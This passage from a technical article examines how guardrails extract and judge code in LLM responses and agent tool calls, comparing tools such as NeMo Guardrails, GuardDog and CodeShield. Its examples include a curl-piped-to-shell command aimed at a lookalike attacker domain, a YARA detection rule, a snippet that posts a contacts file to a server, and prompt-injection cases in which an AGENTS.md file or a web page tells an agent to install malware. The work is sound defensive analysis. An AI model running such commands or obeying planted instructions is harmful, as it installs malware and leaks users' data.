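| Incoming prompt | Usually a guess from the text | Stated by the user, perhaps dishonestly | Usually unknown |
| Retrieved document | A filename may help, if the application kept it | The words are the document author's, not the user's | Usually unknown |
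| Response | A guess, unless the application expects one language | The prompt is available for comparison | Known in a dashboard, unknown in a general chat |
| Tool-call arguments | Often clear from the tool | Available if the guardrail also receives the conversation | Known |
| Moment of execution | Known | Usually lost, unless the application passes it on | Known, along with the account and its permissions |

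Checking prompts is useful for enforcing a complete ban and for refusing harmful requests before the model generates a response. It is a poor way to block malicious code in general, because code in a prompt may go no further than the model. Such a check would often block security staff who paste in malware to have it explained.

The most useful thing to know about a retrieved document may be where it came from. The instruction for a coding agent to install the malicious package came from the AGENTS.md file, not from the user. A check that treats all of the model's input as the user's own words would miss this difference, so the application should record which text came from the user and which came from a web page or file.

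A check on the response covers code that didn't exist when the user wrote the prompt. It can also compare the code with the request if it receives both, as Palo Alto Networks' service does in the John Green example. A match shows that the model did what the user wanted, but not that the request was allowed. The service also accepts code in a separate field, `code_response`, so if an application already has the code on its own, the scanner doesn't have to find it in prose. The documentation asks applications to combine snippets in the same language and to send a separate request for each language.

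For an agent, the arguments of a tool call are usually a better place to check than the response. If the tool is a terminal, the argument is a shell command with no surrounding explanation, and its destination is known. But one argument may not contain the whole program. An agent often writes a script to a file with one tool call and runs it with another, whose argument is little more than the filename. The guardrail has to connect the two calls or inspect the file before it runs. The Acme command contains only the script's address, so the guardrail can't inspect the script until it has been downloaded.

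By the time the shell runs Acme's script, the downloaded code is available to examine. The system can also enforce permissions at this stage, and a monitor can stop individual actions. The usual weakness is missing context. For example, a database may receive only an UPDATE query from the application's account, with nothing to show whether an employee requested it or a prompt injection caused it.

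To address this problem, OWASP's 2026 entry on excessive agency, which covers models with more power than they need, recommends, by Respan's account, sending privileged tool calls through fixed rules outside the model that recheck the intent and arguments at the moment of execution. For that check, the application has to pass along who made the request and what they wanted. The entry also warns about tools that should only read data but connect with an account that can update and delete it. Removing those rights from the dashboard's account would stop John Green's move even if every text check missed the query.

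Steve Wilson, who founded the list, makes a similar point in OWASP's September announcement. He expects models to make mistakes and be tricked from time to time, and wants firm limits on their access, decisions and actions. This is good advice for anyone who runs the database or the agent's shell, and a reason to put the strictest check as late as possible. The owner of a general chat assistant often can't follow it, because the user may paste a command into a terminal on their own computer, which leaves the response as the last place the owner can check.

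## Finding the code inside ordinary text

A checker has to find any code in a response before it can judge whether the code is malicious. In the Acme answer, that means picking 41 characters of shell out of a few sentences of English. The checker usually normalises the characters, decodes anything in a recognised encoding, splits the message into prose and snippets, identifies each snippet's language, and joins the snippets that belong together, in that order. Each step works on the previous step's output, so code missed at one step is also missing from the later ones.

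### Normalising and decoding

Applications usually send prompts and responses as JSON, which encodes a line break inside a string as a backslash followed by the letter n. A sample request in Palo Alto Networks' documentation therefore contains a whole Python program on one long line. Python depends on line breaks and indentation, so the scanner should first run the message through a JSON parser to restore them.

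Normalisation then gives equivalent characters a single form. Unicode, the standard that assigns a number to every character, has several versions of many letters and spaces. For example, text copied from a web page often contains non-breaking spaces, which look like ordinary spaces but have a different number. NFKC, a standard Unicode procedure, converts them to ordinary spaces. It does not change curly quotation marks or zero-width characters, so a scanner needs its own rules for those.

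The normalised copy can differ from what the execution point will read. Python applies NFKC to the names of variables and functions, but a shell doesn't apply it to commands. A shell treats two words joined by a non-breaking space as one word, so a command that the scanner finds in the normalised copy may never run. The scanner should keep the original and examine both versions where they differ.

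Base64, the encoding that caused the false PowerShell alarm described earlier, has many innocent uses, such as embedding small images in web pages. Any four-letter English word is also valid Base64, so "code" decodes to three meaningless bytes. A sensible scanner therefore decodes only long runs of Base64 characters and keeps the result only if it looks like text or a known file format.

Decoded text can contain more encoded text, so the scanner has to decode repeatedly, up to a limit on the number of rounds and the total size. The size limit is needed because some compressed data expands about a thousandfold, so a short message could fill the scanner's memory. A scanner that reaches either limit should report that part of the message is unchecked, because a verdict of "benign" would be misleading. Raising the limits doesn't help with an encoding that the scanner doesn't recognise.

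Decoding can also cause false alarms. If a web page has converted a script so that it displays as text, a scanner that decodes the page will find a script tag, although nothing will run it. The scanner should record whether each snippet came from the original text or a decoded copy, so that someone can check whether any later program does the same decoding.

### Marked code and the 15% rule

Chat models usually format their answers in Markdown, which has syntax for marking code. A fenced block begins and ends with a line of three backticks, and the language's name can follow the opening backticks. Four spaces at the start of a line can also mark code, and a pair of single backticks marks a short piece of code inside a sentence.

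cdot65's *Code Extraction* documents an extractor that relies mainly on these marks. It belongs to an open-source hook for Prisma AIRS, the Palo Alto Networks product that includes the scanning service. (A hook is an add-on that runs automatically at a set point, in this case when a response arrives.) The extractor looks for fenced blocks, then for lines with at least four leading spaces. Only if it finds neither does it look for other signs of code, such as import statements, function definitions, braces, semicolons and shell pipes. It then classifies the content as code if more than 15% of the characters are "code-like".

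Suppose a 2,000-character answer has a 40-character command in the middle of a sentence. Even if every character of the command counts as code-like, the share is only

40 / 2,000 = 2%

To pass the threshold, the answer would need more than 300 characters of code, or the whole message would have to be at most 266 characters long.

The documentation doesn't define "code-like character". If only punctuation counts, 7 of the Acme command's 41 characters (17%) are code-like, so the command would barely qualify even on its own. In a 2,000-character answer, those 7 characters would make up only 0.35% of the text.

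The order of the methods makes this worse. Suppose Acme's answer gives the install command in a sentence and then a harmless version-check command in a fenced block. The extractor finds the fenced block, so it never applies the 15% rule to the rest. Longer, more helpful answers are more likely to contain a fenced block, and a stray command is also easiest to overlook in them.

If the hook misses a command in the text, that command may never be checked for malware. The hook sends prose to the service in a field called `response` and code in `code_response`, and cdot65 explains that the engines for detecting malicious code run only on `code_response`. The service might still find the command through its own extraction of code from plain text, which Palo Alto Networks announced in July 2025.

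Even correct extraction can weaken detection. In cdot65's scheme, the check on web addresses applies to the prose field. The two Acme commands differ only in their addresses, so moving the command into the code field could make it skip the check most likely to tell them apart. The service can evidently check an address inside code, since Palo Alto Networks' sample report on a shell script in a prompt includes a separate verdict on the address from which the script downloads a program. The hook could avoid the problem by sending the complete response in the prose field and a copy of the code in the code field.

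LLM Guard, Protect AI's open-source set of guardrails, depends more on Markdown. Protect AI's *Code Scanner* describes a check that lets an application's owner allow or ban particular programming languages. A trained model identifies the language of each snippet, but the scanner extracts snippets only from Markdown. If a user types a command without Markdown formatting, the scanner doesn't extract it, so the model can't classify it.

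Protect AI recommends the Ban Code scanner instead of the Code scanner for owners who want no code at all. Ban Code is also faster. The Code scanner took nearly three times as long, an average of 63 milliseconds, on the same type of rented server with a prompt of the same length. With a graphics processor and optimised software, the Code scanner's average fell to about 6 milliseconds, so speed is a weak reason to choose between them.

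### Fences that close too early

Models sometimes misplace the fences that mark code blocks. In Markdown, a block that opens with three backticks ends at the next line that contains only three or more backticks. If a model wraps a whole document in such a block, and the document contains a code example with its own fences, the example's closing fence also closes the outer block, and the rest of the document falls outside it. A longer outer fence would prevent this, but models often don't use one.

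Lee and Kang (2026), in *LatentMD*, measured how often this and related mistakes happen. They gave nine models prompts for technical documents, many of them designed to provoke the problem, and 38% of the answers had suitable content but faulty fences. They also ran 16 models on 248 real requests from public chat logs, where the failure rate was 1.97% overall, 17.5% when the model wrapped its whole answer in a fence, and 0.77% when it didn't. The 1.97% figure is the better guide to ordinary use, but it may still be too high for general traffic because Lee and Kang selected requests for Markdown documents likely to contain code.

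Extraction nearly always fails when a code fence inside a document is at least as long as the fence around it. Lee and Kang tested three extractors, including one that parses Markdown properly. The extractors failed to recover the intended code in 1% to 2% of plain documents with correct fences, but in at least 99.8% of answers where the inner fence was too long and the fences still paired up. In one case, Lee and Kang gave Claude Opus 4.5 a request from the chat logs for a four-slide presentation as a Markdown file. The extractor returned only lines 2 to 22 of the 95-line answer, stopping in the middle of a code example on the second slide.

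Lines of code left outside the fences are dangerous because a malware scanner will treat them as prose. The scanner should therefore use fences as hints about where code is likely to be, and keep searching the text outside them even after it finds one.

An application that runs code from model responses has its own extractor, and the guardrail should extract the same text. For example, the `extract_code` function in hbllmutils, a Python library for handling model responses, returns the contents of any fenced blocks, or the entire reply if there are none. A guardrail that scans only fenced blocks would therefore miss all the code in an unfenced reply, which the application would still run. The simplest solution is to scan exactly what the application's function returns, just before the application runs it.

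### Code without marks

Long before chatbots, software researchers wanted to separate code from prose in emails and bug reports, which often don't mark where code starts and ends. Early systems used hand-written patterns. These can work very well on one project, but adapting them to another takes expertise, so later researchers trained classifiers on examples.

Mäntylä, Calefato and Claes (2018), in *Natural Language or Not (NLoN)*, classified text one line at a time. They labelled 2,000 lines from each of three sources: comments in Mozilla's bug tracker, chat messages from the Kubernetes software project, and emails from the Apache Lucene project. Their classifier combines three-character sequences with 11 simple measurements, such as the share of special characters and the number of very common English words. Its AUC was between 0.976 and 0.987. An AUC of 0.98 means a randomly chosen line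 of prose gets a higher prose score than a randomly chosen line of anything else 98% of the time.

Results varied more when the classifier had no training lines from the source being tested. The AUC was 0.980 for Mozilla's comments but 0.913 for the Lucene emails. Mäntylä and colleagues recommend labelling 2,000 lines from each new source, which they estimate takes about four hours. This is little work for a company protecting one application, and the recommendation is probably the most useful practical advice in this research.

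In the test data, any line that mixes prose and code is labelled as prose. The sentence "Run `curl https://acme.example/install.sh | sh` in your terminal." would therefore be labelled as prose. A classifier could get a perfect score on this test and miss every inline command.

A newer line classifier probably loses accuracy on prose unlike its training data. Yotkova, Kastreva and colleagues (2026), in *FMI_SU_Yotkova_Kastreva at SemEval-2026 Task 13*, trained it on code from Stack Overflow and prose from chat on Twitch, a video-streaming site, as part of a system for recognising machine-written code. It was 97.1% accurate on held-out data of the same kind, but 89.5% on 30 examples that they labelled by hand from the competition's test set. With so few examples, the second figure could easily be off by ten percentage points, and some of the errors involved repetitive strings that even a person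 might not know how to classify. Still, a drop is likely on an assistant's answers, because their prose is so different from Twitch chat.

Finding code within a line requires labelling units smaller than a line. Chrupała (2013), in *Text segmentation with character-level text embeddings*, labelled every character in Stack Overflow questions as prose, part of a code block, or part of an inline snippet. A basic version, trained on 10 million characters, had an F1 score of 88% for blocks and 14% for inline code. It correctly marked the boundaries of only 9% of inline snippets. Features learned by a neural network raised the score for blocks from 86% to 91% on the final test.

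The task is probably easier than the 14% score suggests, because Chrupała took the correct answers from the formatting applied by Stack Overflow's users, who marked inline code very inconsistently. The score also penalises boundary errors of even one character, whereas a security scanner can tolerate an extra word at either end of a command. Still, the result suggests that a good score on code blocks is little evidence of how well a method finds inline commands.

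*POSIT* (Pârțachi, Dash and colleagues, 2020) labels each word or symbol with both its language and its grammatical role, for example as an English verb or a variable in a program. It improved accuracy on language identification by 10.6% over the previous best method. Labelling each word suits the Acme sentence much better than labelling whole lines, but the researchers built *POSIT* for reusing and tracing code in developers' discussions, not for finding attacks.

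An improvement that takes less computation is to apply a rule like the hook's to each sentence instead of the whole message. The Acme command makes up 41 of the 63 characters in "Run … in your terminal.", or 65%, however long the rest of the answer is. If only punctuation counts, the share is about 13%, so the threshold would need adjusting. A lower threshold will also pick up harmless sentences with long web addresses, but that may be acceptable at this stage because a later check will determine whether the text is malicious. The pattern-based code detectors in garak, an open-source tool for testing language models, are also designed to find as much code as possible, even if that means more mistakes.

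### Naming the language

Once the scanner has a snippet, it must identify the language to choose suitable rules or a parser. The language name on a code fence's opening line is a useful clue, but *WildCode Revisited* found that these names were often missing or wrong in real ChatGPT conversations, so it supplemented them with a trained language identifier.

Programming-language identifiers often have excellent published scores. Hugging Face reports an F1 score above 0.999 for *CodeBERTa-language-id* on its own evaluation data and describes the task as relatively easy. Random snippets from the web are much harder. *Stack Overflow Meets Replication* checked the labels of 385 such snippets by hand and found that GPT-4o, a general language model from 2024, was right 93% of the time and Guesslang only 55%. The paper considers GPT-4o too expensive for its collection of 20 million snippets, but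 a company that scans a few thousand responses a day might be able to afford it.

Guesslang also rarely fails to return a label. In *Geographic Variation in Stack Overflow Code Quality* (2026), it labeled more than 6 million snippets and returned no language for 4,551. If its accuracy there was near 55%, nearly all its mistakes were wrong labels, passed to the next program with no sign of error.

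A tool's accuracy on whole files is a poor predictor of its accuracy on snippets. *SCC* (2018) compared a simple statistical classifier with a commercial tool whose claimed accuracy on source files was 99.4%. The simple classifier did better on Stack Overflow snippets, but the comparison covered only 150 of them because the researchers had to pay for each use of the commercial tool.

The programming language of a short snippet is harder to identify. *Predicting the Programming Language of Questions and Snippets of StackOverflow* (2018) reports that accuracy rose as the minimum snippet length increased from 10 to 100 characters. Using the words of the question along with the code improved accuracy by 14% over code alone, so an extractor that discards the prose loses useful evidence. In the Acme answer, the words "in your terminal" suggest a shell command more clearly than some commands would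 on their own.

In *programming language identification*, philomath-1209 trained LLM Guard's identifier on nearly 26,000 examples in 26 languages from Rosetta Code, a site that collects solutions to the same programming tasks in many languages. The 26 languages include COBOL and Fortran but not Shell, Batch or SQL. The published sample code picks the most probable of the 26 labels, so it will mislabel a shell command.

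*WildCode Revisited* used the same identifier, which has a reported accuracy of 95%. It labelled 1,935 untagged snippets as PHP, a language for web servers, but none was valid PHP. The researchers found that all of them involved command-line tools associated with PHP. Such errors could seriously affect a malware scanner, which would apply PHP rules to terminal commands. The identifier also covers only four of the seven languages that Palo Alto Networks' malicious-code check supports, so it would be a poor choice for sorting snippets before sending them to that check.

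Yotkova and colleagues built a programming-language identifier that agreed with 95.1% of the labels on 1,000 examples, though the labels came from an OpenAI model, not from people. It most often confused C with C++ and C# with Java. These mistakes matter less than others because the paired languages have such similar grammars that the parser's output remained usable. Overall accuracy weights all mistakes equally, so a defender should check which languages a tool confuses, and especially how it labels shell commands.

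Parsing a snippet is an unreliable way to check its label because snippets are often incomplete. The standard Java compiler, for example, will normally reject a method copied without the class around it, even if the method is ordinary Java. In *WildCode Revisited*, more than a third of the untagged snippets that the identifier labelled as Python, JavaScript or C# failed a syntax check. A failure can mean a wrong label, a missing piece or a real mistake in the code, and the check alone can't show which. Yotkova and colleagues used Tree-sitter, a parser that marks the parts it can't interpret and parses the rest, so it suits fragments much better than a compiler.

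If text parses as a shell command, that is only weak evidence that it is code. A shell's grammar accepts "please delete the old file" as a call to a program named `please` with four arguments. That program probably doesn't exist, but the parser doesn't check whether it does.

### A file type for text that had none

Palo Alto Networks' service returns a report on the code it extracts. According to the company, a list called `all_code_blocks` contains the text of every snippet taken from the prompt or response. A second list gives a hash and a `file_type` for the code the service analysed. The sample report contains one block, a shell script with the file type "Shell". The sample request printed above it contains a Python program that writes the EICAR test string to a file. The request and the report come from different scans, so the report doesn't show the service's result for that program.

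The text field had no file type, so the service worked out the language and recorded it under a name meant for files, presumably because its malware engines expect files. This is a practical way to reuse those engines, and it lets each type of code in a mixed message have its own label. But the label is still guessed from the content. The sample report gives no confidence figure for it, so someone reading the logs could easily mistake "Shell" for a fact about the input.

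The SHA-256 hash is a fingerprint of the code. Identical text always gives the same hash, so a defender can quickly search old logs for a snippet that has just proved malicious. But even one extra blank line changes the hash completely, and small differences are common in extracted code. Yotkova and colleagues found that about 5,000 of 500,000 samples began with a stray line such as "python", apparently left over from Markdown. Removing such leftovers before hashing would make matches more reliable, as long as the original text also stays in the log.

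The sample report also doesn't give the position of each snippet. The same service's report on sensitive data gives the start and end of every match, so the service can mask a credit card number and leave the rest of the message readable. If the report gave positions for code too, an application could remove one command from a long answer instead of blocking all of it.

### Joining pieces of code

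Two snippets that look harmless separately can form a harmful program, so a scanner should examine related snippets together. For instance, one might collect saved passwords into a file, and another might upload a file to a server. Palo Alto Networks asks callers to combine snippets in the same language into one request, so the caller has to identify each snippet's language before the service does, and a mistake will put a snippet in the wrong request.

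cdot65's hook records the languages it detects, but its documentation describes joining all the blocks into one `code_response` field, with a line of three hyphens between them. An answer with both Python and shell commands would then arrive as a mixture. In Python, a line of three hyphens is also a syntax error, which could stop a strict parser. A comment in the snippet's own language would be a safer separator.

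Deciding which snippets belong together is harder across a whole conversation. A user may paste half a script into the prompt and ask the model to write the rest, or request one function today and another tomorrow. Scanning the prompt and response separately will miss a program split between them. A reasonable default is to scan each snippet alone and also scan all of them joined in the order they appeared. Trying every order isn't realistic, since ten snippets can be arranged in 3,628,800 ways.

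Joining all the code snippets in a conversation before scanning them can produce misleading results. *WildCode Revisited* interprets the several snippets in a typical coding conversation as a sign that users keep asking for revisions. If so, the joined text would contain several versions of one program, and might combine a line from an abandoned draft with one from its replacement. When an agent writes the code, the guardrail can avoid guessing which snippets belong together by inspecting the finished file before it runs.

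When an application displays a response while the model is still writing it, a command can begin in one batch of text and end in the next. The scanner has to hold back the last line until it is complete, or check the growing response again each time more text arrives. By then, a user may already have copied the command.

### Instructions that become code later

Some harmful messages contain no code snippet. A web page might tell an agent in plain English to download the setup script from a certain address and run it, and the agent can write the `curl` command itself. An extractor that returns nothing for this page is working correctly, and lowering the threshold from 15% to 1% would make no difference.

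When a prompt tells an agent in prose to run something, the code doesn't exist until the agent writes its tool call. A check for prompt injection might notice the instruction earlier, but legitimate installation guides contain the same sentence. After the agent writes the call, most of the extraction work is unnecessary, because the command is already separate from the prose and the choice of tool usually indicates the command's language.

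## Judging code with rules and static analysis

Once a scanner has separated a command from the surrounding text, it has to determine whether the command is malicious. The simplest method is to compare the command with patterns written in advance.

### A rule for the install command

A signature rule is a stated pattern of strings and conditions that counts as a detection when text matches it. Malware analysts often write these rules for YARA, a free pattern-matching tool. A YARA rule usually has a list of strings to look for and a condition that combines the results with words such as `and`, `or` and `not`. This rule looks for commands that download a script and pass it to a shell:

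```
rule download_piped_to_shell
{
    strings:
        $fetch = "curl" fullword
        $pipe  = /\|\s*(ba)?sh\b/
    condition:
        $fetch and $pipe
}
```

The first string is the word "curl", and the modifier `fullword` rules out matches inside longer words, such as "curly". The second string is a regular expression, a compact notation for patterns of characters. It matches a vertical bar, then any amount of space, then `sh` or `bash`. The rule matches if both strings appear anywhere in the text.

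The rule matches both Acme's own install command and the command with the criminal's address, because both contain "curl" and "| sh". Without the rule, both commands get through. The rule would also flag the install command on the home page of a malware scanner, Atomdrift's *Zero-day malware detection on your own hardware*, which has the same form.

A rule needs information about the address to separate the two Acme commands. A defender who has learned of the attack can add the string "acme-update.example" and require all three strings. The rule then flags only the malicious command, but it will miss the attack once the criminal switches to another domain.

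The defender could instead list Acme's genuine address as an exception, but this is easy to get wrong. Suppose the condition includes "and not" followed by a string for `acme.example`. If a response links to Acme's real website and then gives the criminal's command, the exception would apply because the genuine address is somewhere in the text. The rule should therefore check the address inside the command.

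Rules can also catch a bad address before anyone reports it. In *From single pull requests to full software packages*, Doutre, Peronnet and colleagues describe a system at the monitoring company Datadog that uses language models to find malicious code. The first-pass model sometimes accepted domains that only resembled Datadog's, so the team added a step that extracts every domain and compares it with a list of lookalikes generated from Datadog's real ones. Acme could do the same for its own name, and its list might well include `acme-update.example`. A general chat assistant would need such lists for hundreds of tools, along with each tool's genuine domains.

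### NeMo Guardrails and the weather script

NeMo Guardrails, a library from the chip company NVIDIA, applies YARA rules to model output. NVIDIA's *Agentic Security* describes four default rule sets and recommends each for a particular use of the output:

| Rule set | What it covers | When to use it |
|---|---|---|
| `code` | Python code injection | The output goes to a code interpreter or becomes an argument to another function |
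| `sqli` | SQL injection | The output becomes part of a database query |
| `template` | Injection into Jinja, a template engine | Jinja renders the output |
| `xss` | Scripts in Markdown and JavaScript | A page displays the output directly as HTML or Markdown |

This arrangement suits text fields because the application's owner chooses the rules by execution point, so the software doesn't have to infer where the text will go. None of the four sets is for shell commands in general, so the defaults would probably let both Acme commands through. Owners can add their own rules, such as the one above.

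When a rule matches, the owner can have the library either reject the response or omit the matching text. Rejecting replaces the whole response with a refusal that names the rule set. NVIDIA calls this the safest action and recommends it for production. Omitting keeps the rest of a long answer but can have odd results. If the library removed exactly the two strings in the download rule, the user would see a bare web address with no explanation. Removing part of a database query could leave a different query that still runs. A third action, "sanitize", is meant to make the text harmless without deleting it, but according to NVIDIA's *nemoguardrails.library.injection_detection.actions* it currently only produces an error.

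In one example, NVIDIA describes a request for a Python script that gets the weather in Santa Clara as "possibly unsafe". The output shown is a complete, ordinary weather script, which the guardrail did not block. This is probably because the example configuration omits the setting that applies the check to output, although NVIDIA says on the same page that this setting is necessary.

NVIDIA's *Detecting Injection Attacks with Guardrails* includes the setting and makes almost the same request. This time the guardrail refuses, citing the `code` rules. The tutorial explains that these rules cover Python code that uses shells or networking, and says a script with networking packages is likely to trigger them. A harmless weather script therefore matches because it contacts a weather service.

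Whether blocking the script is a mistake depends on the application. If a code interpreter should never contact the internet, blocking it is sensible. In a chat assistant that only displays code, it is a false alarm, which the owner could avoid by leaving the `code` set off. Both of NVIDIA's examples turn on all four sets, and a reader could easily copy an example without considering whether their application needs every set.

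The tutorial also checks that the guardrail allows safe content, but its example is a request for 50 words about a stretch of coast in North Carolina. A better test would use harmless code of the kind the application's users request.

NVIDIA says injection detection is meant mainly for agents, to "enhance other security controls as part of a defense-in-depth strategy." It doesn't recommend relying on these rules alone.

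### Parsing code and following its data

A text rule can't distinguish an instruction from a mention of it. TrueFoundry, which sells a gateway between applications and models, lists `eval(` among its patterns for dangerous Python and rates it critical because the function executes whatever string it receives. The pattern also matches tutorials that warn against using `eval()`.

Static analysis, which examines code without running it, can avoid some of these mistakes by parsing the code first. A parser uses the programming language's grammar to turn the text into a tree of statements, function calls and arguments. Trail of Bits' *30 new Semgrep rules* (2024) shows why this matters using Semgrep, a tool that can search code with or without a parser. The test file contains two calls to `os.system`, a Python function that passes a command to the shell, but one is commented out and will never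 run. Semgrep's Python mode reports only the call that isn't commented out. Its plain-text mode gives a different result because it can't recognise comments.

After parsing, an analyser can follow data through the program. The defender names the sources, where sensitive or untrusted data enters, and the sinks, which are functions that could do harm with it. Consider this short program:

```
contacts = open("contacts.txt").read()
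report = contacts.upper()
requests.post("https://stats.example", data=report)
```

If reading that file counts as a source, the analyser marks `contacts` on the first line. The second line converts `contacts` to capitals and stores the result in `report`, so the analyser marks `report` too. The third line sends `report` to a server. If sending data over the network counts as a sink, the analyser reports the marked data's path from the file to the server.

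If the third line sent only the program's version number, a text rule that looks for `open` and `requests.post` would still match, but the analyser would report nothing because the contacts never leave the computer. Tracking where data goes therefore removes false alarms caused by unrelated lines in the same program.

Static analysis can't show whether the owner wants the contacts sent. A backup program also sends files to a server. *Purple Llama CYBERSECEVAL* (Bhatt, Chennabasappa and colleagues, 2023) makes the same point with a script that encrypts a home directory, which could protect its owner's files or hold them to ransom. Similarly, an analyser that parses shell can establish that each of the Acme commands downloads data and passes it to `sh`. This description is more reliable than two matching strings, but it is the same for both commands.

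### How GuardDog combines weak signals

A detector can look for suspicious combinations of behaviours when one alone is not enough to show malice. GuardDog, Datadog's free scanner for malicious software packages, works this way. According to Datadog's *Introducing GuardDog 3.0* (2026), earlier versions listed every match separately, without indicating how likely the package was to be malicious. Version 3.0, released in June 2026, uses two kinds of rules. Capability rules describe what the code can do, such as contact the network or read the clipboard. Threat rules match suspicious details, such as the names of files that hold passwords or domains with unusual endings.

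According to Datadog's *GuardDog* page for version 3.2.0, a high-risk finding needs a capability and a threat in the same file. If they are in different files, the finding counts for less. Either alone can be harmless, since a library for making web requests ought to contact the network, and a suspicious domain might just be in a test or in documentation.

GuardDog then gives the package a score from 0 to 10. The severity of the worst finding and how specific the matches are to malware count for 30% each. The attack's completeness and sophistication count for 20% each. A complete attack has several stages, such as running at installation, collecting passwords and sending them away.

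This weighting is a problem for short snippets, which usually show only one stage. If the score is a simple weighted sum, a snippet with full marks for severity and specificity but none for the other two factors would get

10 × (0.3 + 0.3) = 6

In Datadog's release article, scores from 5 to 7 are suspicious and higher ones are likely malicious. The page for version 3.2.0 puts the upper boundary at 7.5 and limits the high-risk label to attacks with several stages, so a one-line download command would be unlikely to receive that label, even if the script it downloads is dangerous. The difference matters to anyone who blocks packages by label, since a package that scores 7.2 is "likely malicious" according to the article but medium risk according to the version 3.2.0 page.

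Version 3.0 also replaced Semgrep with YARA. Datadog found that Semgrep used a lot of memory on large files and was slow on packages with many files, partly because it started a new process for each scan. An early test version that still used Semgrep skipped files over 10 MB and allowed each rule 10 seconds per file, according to the *GuardDog* page for that version. Datadog's Semgrep rules also fitted particular malware samples too closely and missed new ones.

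The second complaint is about how Datadog wrote its rules, and a YARA rule can be just as narrow. GuardDog also lost parsing when it dropped Semgrep, so its source-code rules can match comments. That seems reasonable for a scanner that needs several signals before it raises a serious alarm, but it would be worse for a guardrail that blocks a response on a single match.

### GuardDog's results

Datadog tests GuardDog every night on packages known to be harmless or malicious. Its collection of more than 27,000 malicious packages includes many that are nearly identical, so a random sample could consist mostly of near-copies. Datadog therefore groups similar packages with TLSH, a hash that gives similar values for similar files, and samples from the groups. Tests of detectors on model output should also group similar samples, because models often write many slight variations of one script.

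The release article also shows two scans. React, a popular JavaScript library, scored 0.0, while a compromised release of LiteLLM, a library for calling language models, scored 10.0, with 30 separate risks. These are good demonstrations, but two chosen examples are little evidence of the error rates.

GuardDog did much worse in an outside comparison. In November 2026, Atomdrift ran several detectors on 196 malware samples that had first appeared less than 48 hours earlier, with a median age of eight hours. With a cut-off score of 7, GuardDog 3.2.0 caught 13.8% of the malware and flagged none of 196 harmless files. With a cut-off of 5, it caught 16.8% and flagged one harmless file.

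Atomdrift makes a rival scanner, though it publishes every sample and verdict. The comparison counts files that a tool doesn't support as misses. GuardDog is mainly meant for packages from software registries, and only 76 of the 196 malware samples were such packages. Its 13.8% represents 27 samples. Even if all 27 were registry packages, GuardDog would have caught only about 36% of the 76. Some of the 76 came from registries that it doesn't cover, so the figure for packages it could have scanned is probably somewhat higher.

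Wizwand's *Malicious package evaluation dataset*, a page that collects benchmark results, lists a January 2026 test in which a pre-3.0 version of GuardDog caught 85.4% of the malicious packages. Its precision was 67.5%, so about a third of its alarms were false. The two tests used different versions and different samples, so they don't show that GuardDog got worse. But the results differ enough that a good score on one collection of malware is weak evidence of how well a tool will do on new code.

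The low figure shouldn't count against rules in general either. Malcontent, another scanner that uses YARA rules, caught 33.7% of the malware in Atomdrift's test at its strictest setting and 64.8% at a looser one. The looser setting raised its false positive rate from 0.5% to 6.1%.

By default, GuardDog doesn't apply its YARA rules to files whose names end in `.txt`, `.md`, `.json`, `.html` or `.sql`. It would therefore skip the AGENTS.md file that contained instructions for a coding agent to install malware, and any code snippet that an application had saved as `response.txt`. A snippet also has no package name, version history or maintainer, so GuardDog's rules about those wouldn't apply.

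The scanner can also be a target. Several flaws reported in Datadog's GuardDog could have let a malicious package read or write files, or run code, on the computer scanning it. GuardDog 3.0 now unpacks and scans packages in a sandbox without network access. A guardrail that decodes and parses untrusted text should have similarly few permissions.

### CodeShield looks for insecure code

CodeShield is a static-analysis tool built for model responses. Meta first released it with its Llama 3 models. It is now part of LlamaFirewall, a set of agent guardrails that Meta uses in production (Chennabasappa, Nikolaidis and colleagues, *LlamaFirewall*, 2025).

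CodeShield checks responses in two stages to keep the delay short. The first stage uses simple patterns and light analysis. Meta found that it settled about 90% of inputs, typically in under 70 milliseconds. If the first stage finds a possible problem, a more thorough analysis follows, and the total can exceed 300 milliseconds. Taking 70 and 300 as typical values, the average delay is

0.9 × 70 + 0.1 × 300 = 93 milliseconds

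Few users would notice that in a chat. But the saving also means that the thorough analysis never examines code that the first stage passes by mistake.

According to Meta, the rules come from its Insecure Code Detector. Bhatt and colleagues tested the detector on 50 model-written code samples per programming language, which they labelled by hand. It had 96% precision and 79% recall, so nearly all the code it flagged was insecure, but it missed about one insecure sample in five.

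The detector's recall may be lower in ordinary use, because Bhatt and colleagues built their test prompts from open-source code in which the same detector had already found a problem. The models' answers were therefore likely to contain the kinds of flaw the detector has rules for.

Neither figure measures the detection of malicious code, because the detector's roughly 189 patterns all describe insecure programming. Meta's page also lists protection from malicious code that results from prompt injection, but only "in conjunction with other scanners". The eight languages that Bhatt and colleagues list don't include shell, PowerShell or SQL, so CodeShield probably wouldn't flag the Acme commands or the sales dashboard's queries.

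CodeShield seems useful for its actual purpose, which is finding insecure code. When it flags something, Meta suggests either blocking the response or adding a warning. A warning makes sense for insecure code because a programmer can fix the flaw and use the rest. It is weak protection against malicious code, especially if an agent will run the code without anyone reading the warning.

### Snippets with missing parts

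The previous steps often produce incomplete code, which causes more trouble for static analysis than for text rules. Even if a parser can handle the fragment, following its data may be impossible. Take this line, copied from the middle of a program:

`requests.post(address, data=payload)`

A snippet may send `payload` to `address` without including the lines that define either one, so a static analyser can find the sink, where the data is sent, but not the source it came from. Flagging every such snippet would flag a great deal of ordinary web programming, while reporting only complete paths from source to sink would miss a password stealer whose first half is in another snippet.

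A text rule for `requests.post` works equally well on a code fragment and a whole program, which is a good reason to keep some text rules even where a parser is available. Bhatt and colleagues designed their detector for code that is incomplete or won't parse, and it uses both regular expressions and rules that depend on a language's grammar.

Splitting code also affects its GuardDog score. If an application saves each snippet from a response as a separate file, GuardDog will give a capability in one file and a threat in another less weight than if both were in the same file. Joining snippets that belong to the same program before scanning would avoid this.

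When an analyser can't parse a snippet, the guardrail should log the failure and fall back on text rules. Treating "no findings" as "safe" is a serious mistake if the analysis never ran.

### Why hashes and reputation lists miss new code

A hash lookup checks whether the scanner has seen exactly the same code before, and a reputation list shows whether anyone has reported a package, domain or file. Both are fast and rarely flag anything harmless, but they depend on an existing record.

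These checks work well on malware that spreads as identical copies, but usually not on code from a language model, because a model can rename variables or reorder steps each time it writes the same program. Each version has a new hash, and the first victim may be the only person who receives it. Honestcue, the malware that requests code from Gemini, could run a program that exists nowhere else.

Even conventional malware is often too new to appear on reputation lists. Socket, a company that tracks malicious packages, could look up 72 of the samples in Atomdrift's comparison and had a record for only 36. It had no record of any of the harmless packages, so its false positive rate of zero doesn't show that it examined them and judged them correctly.

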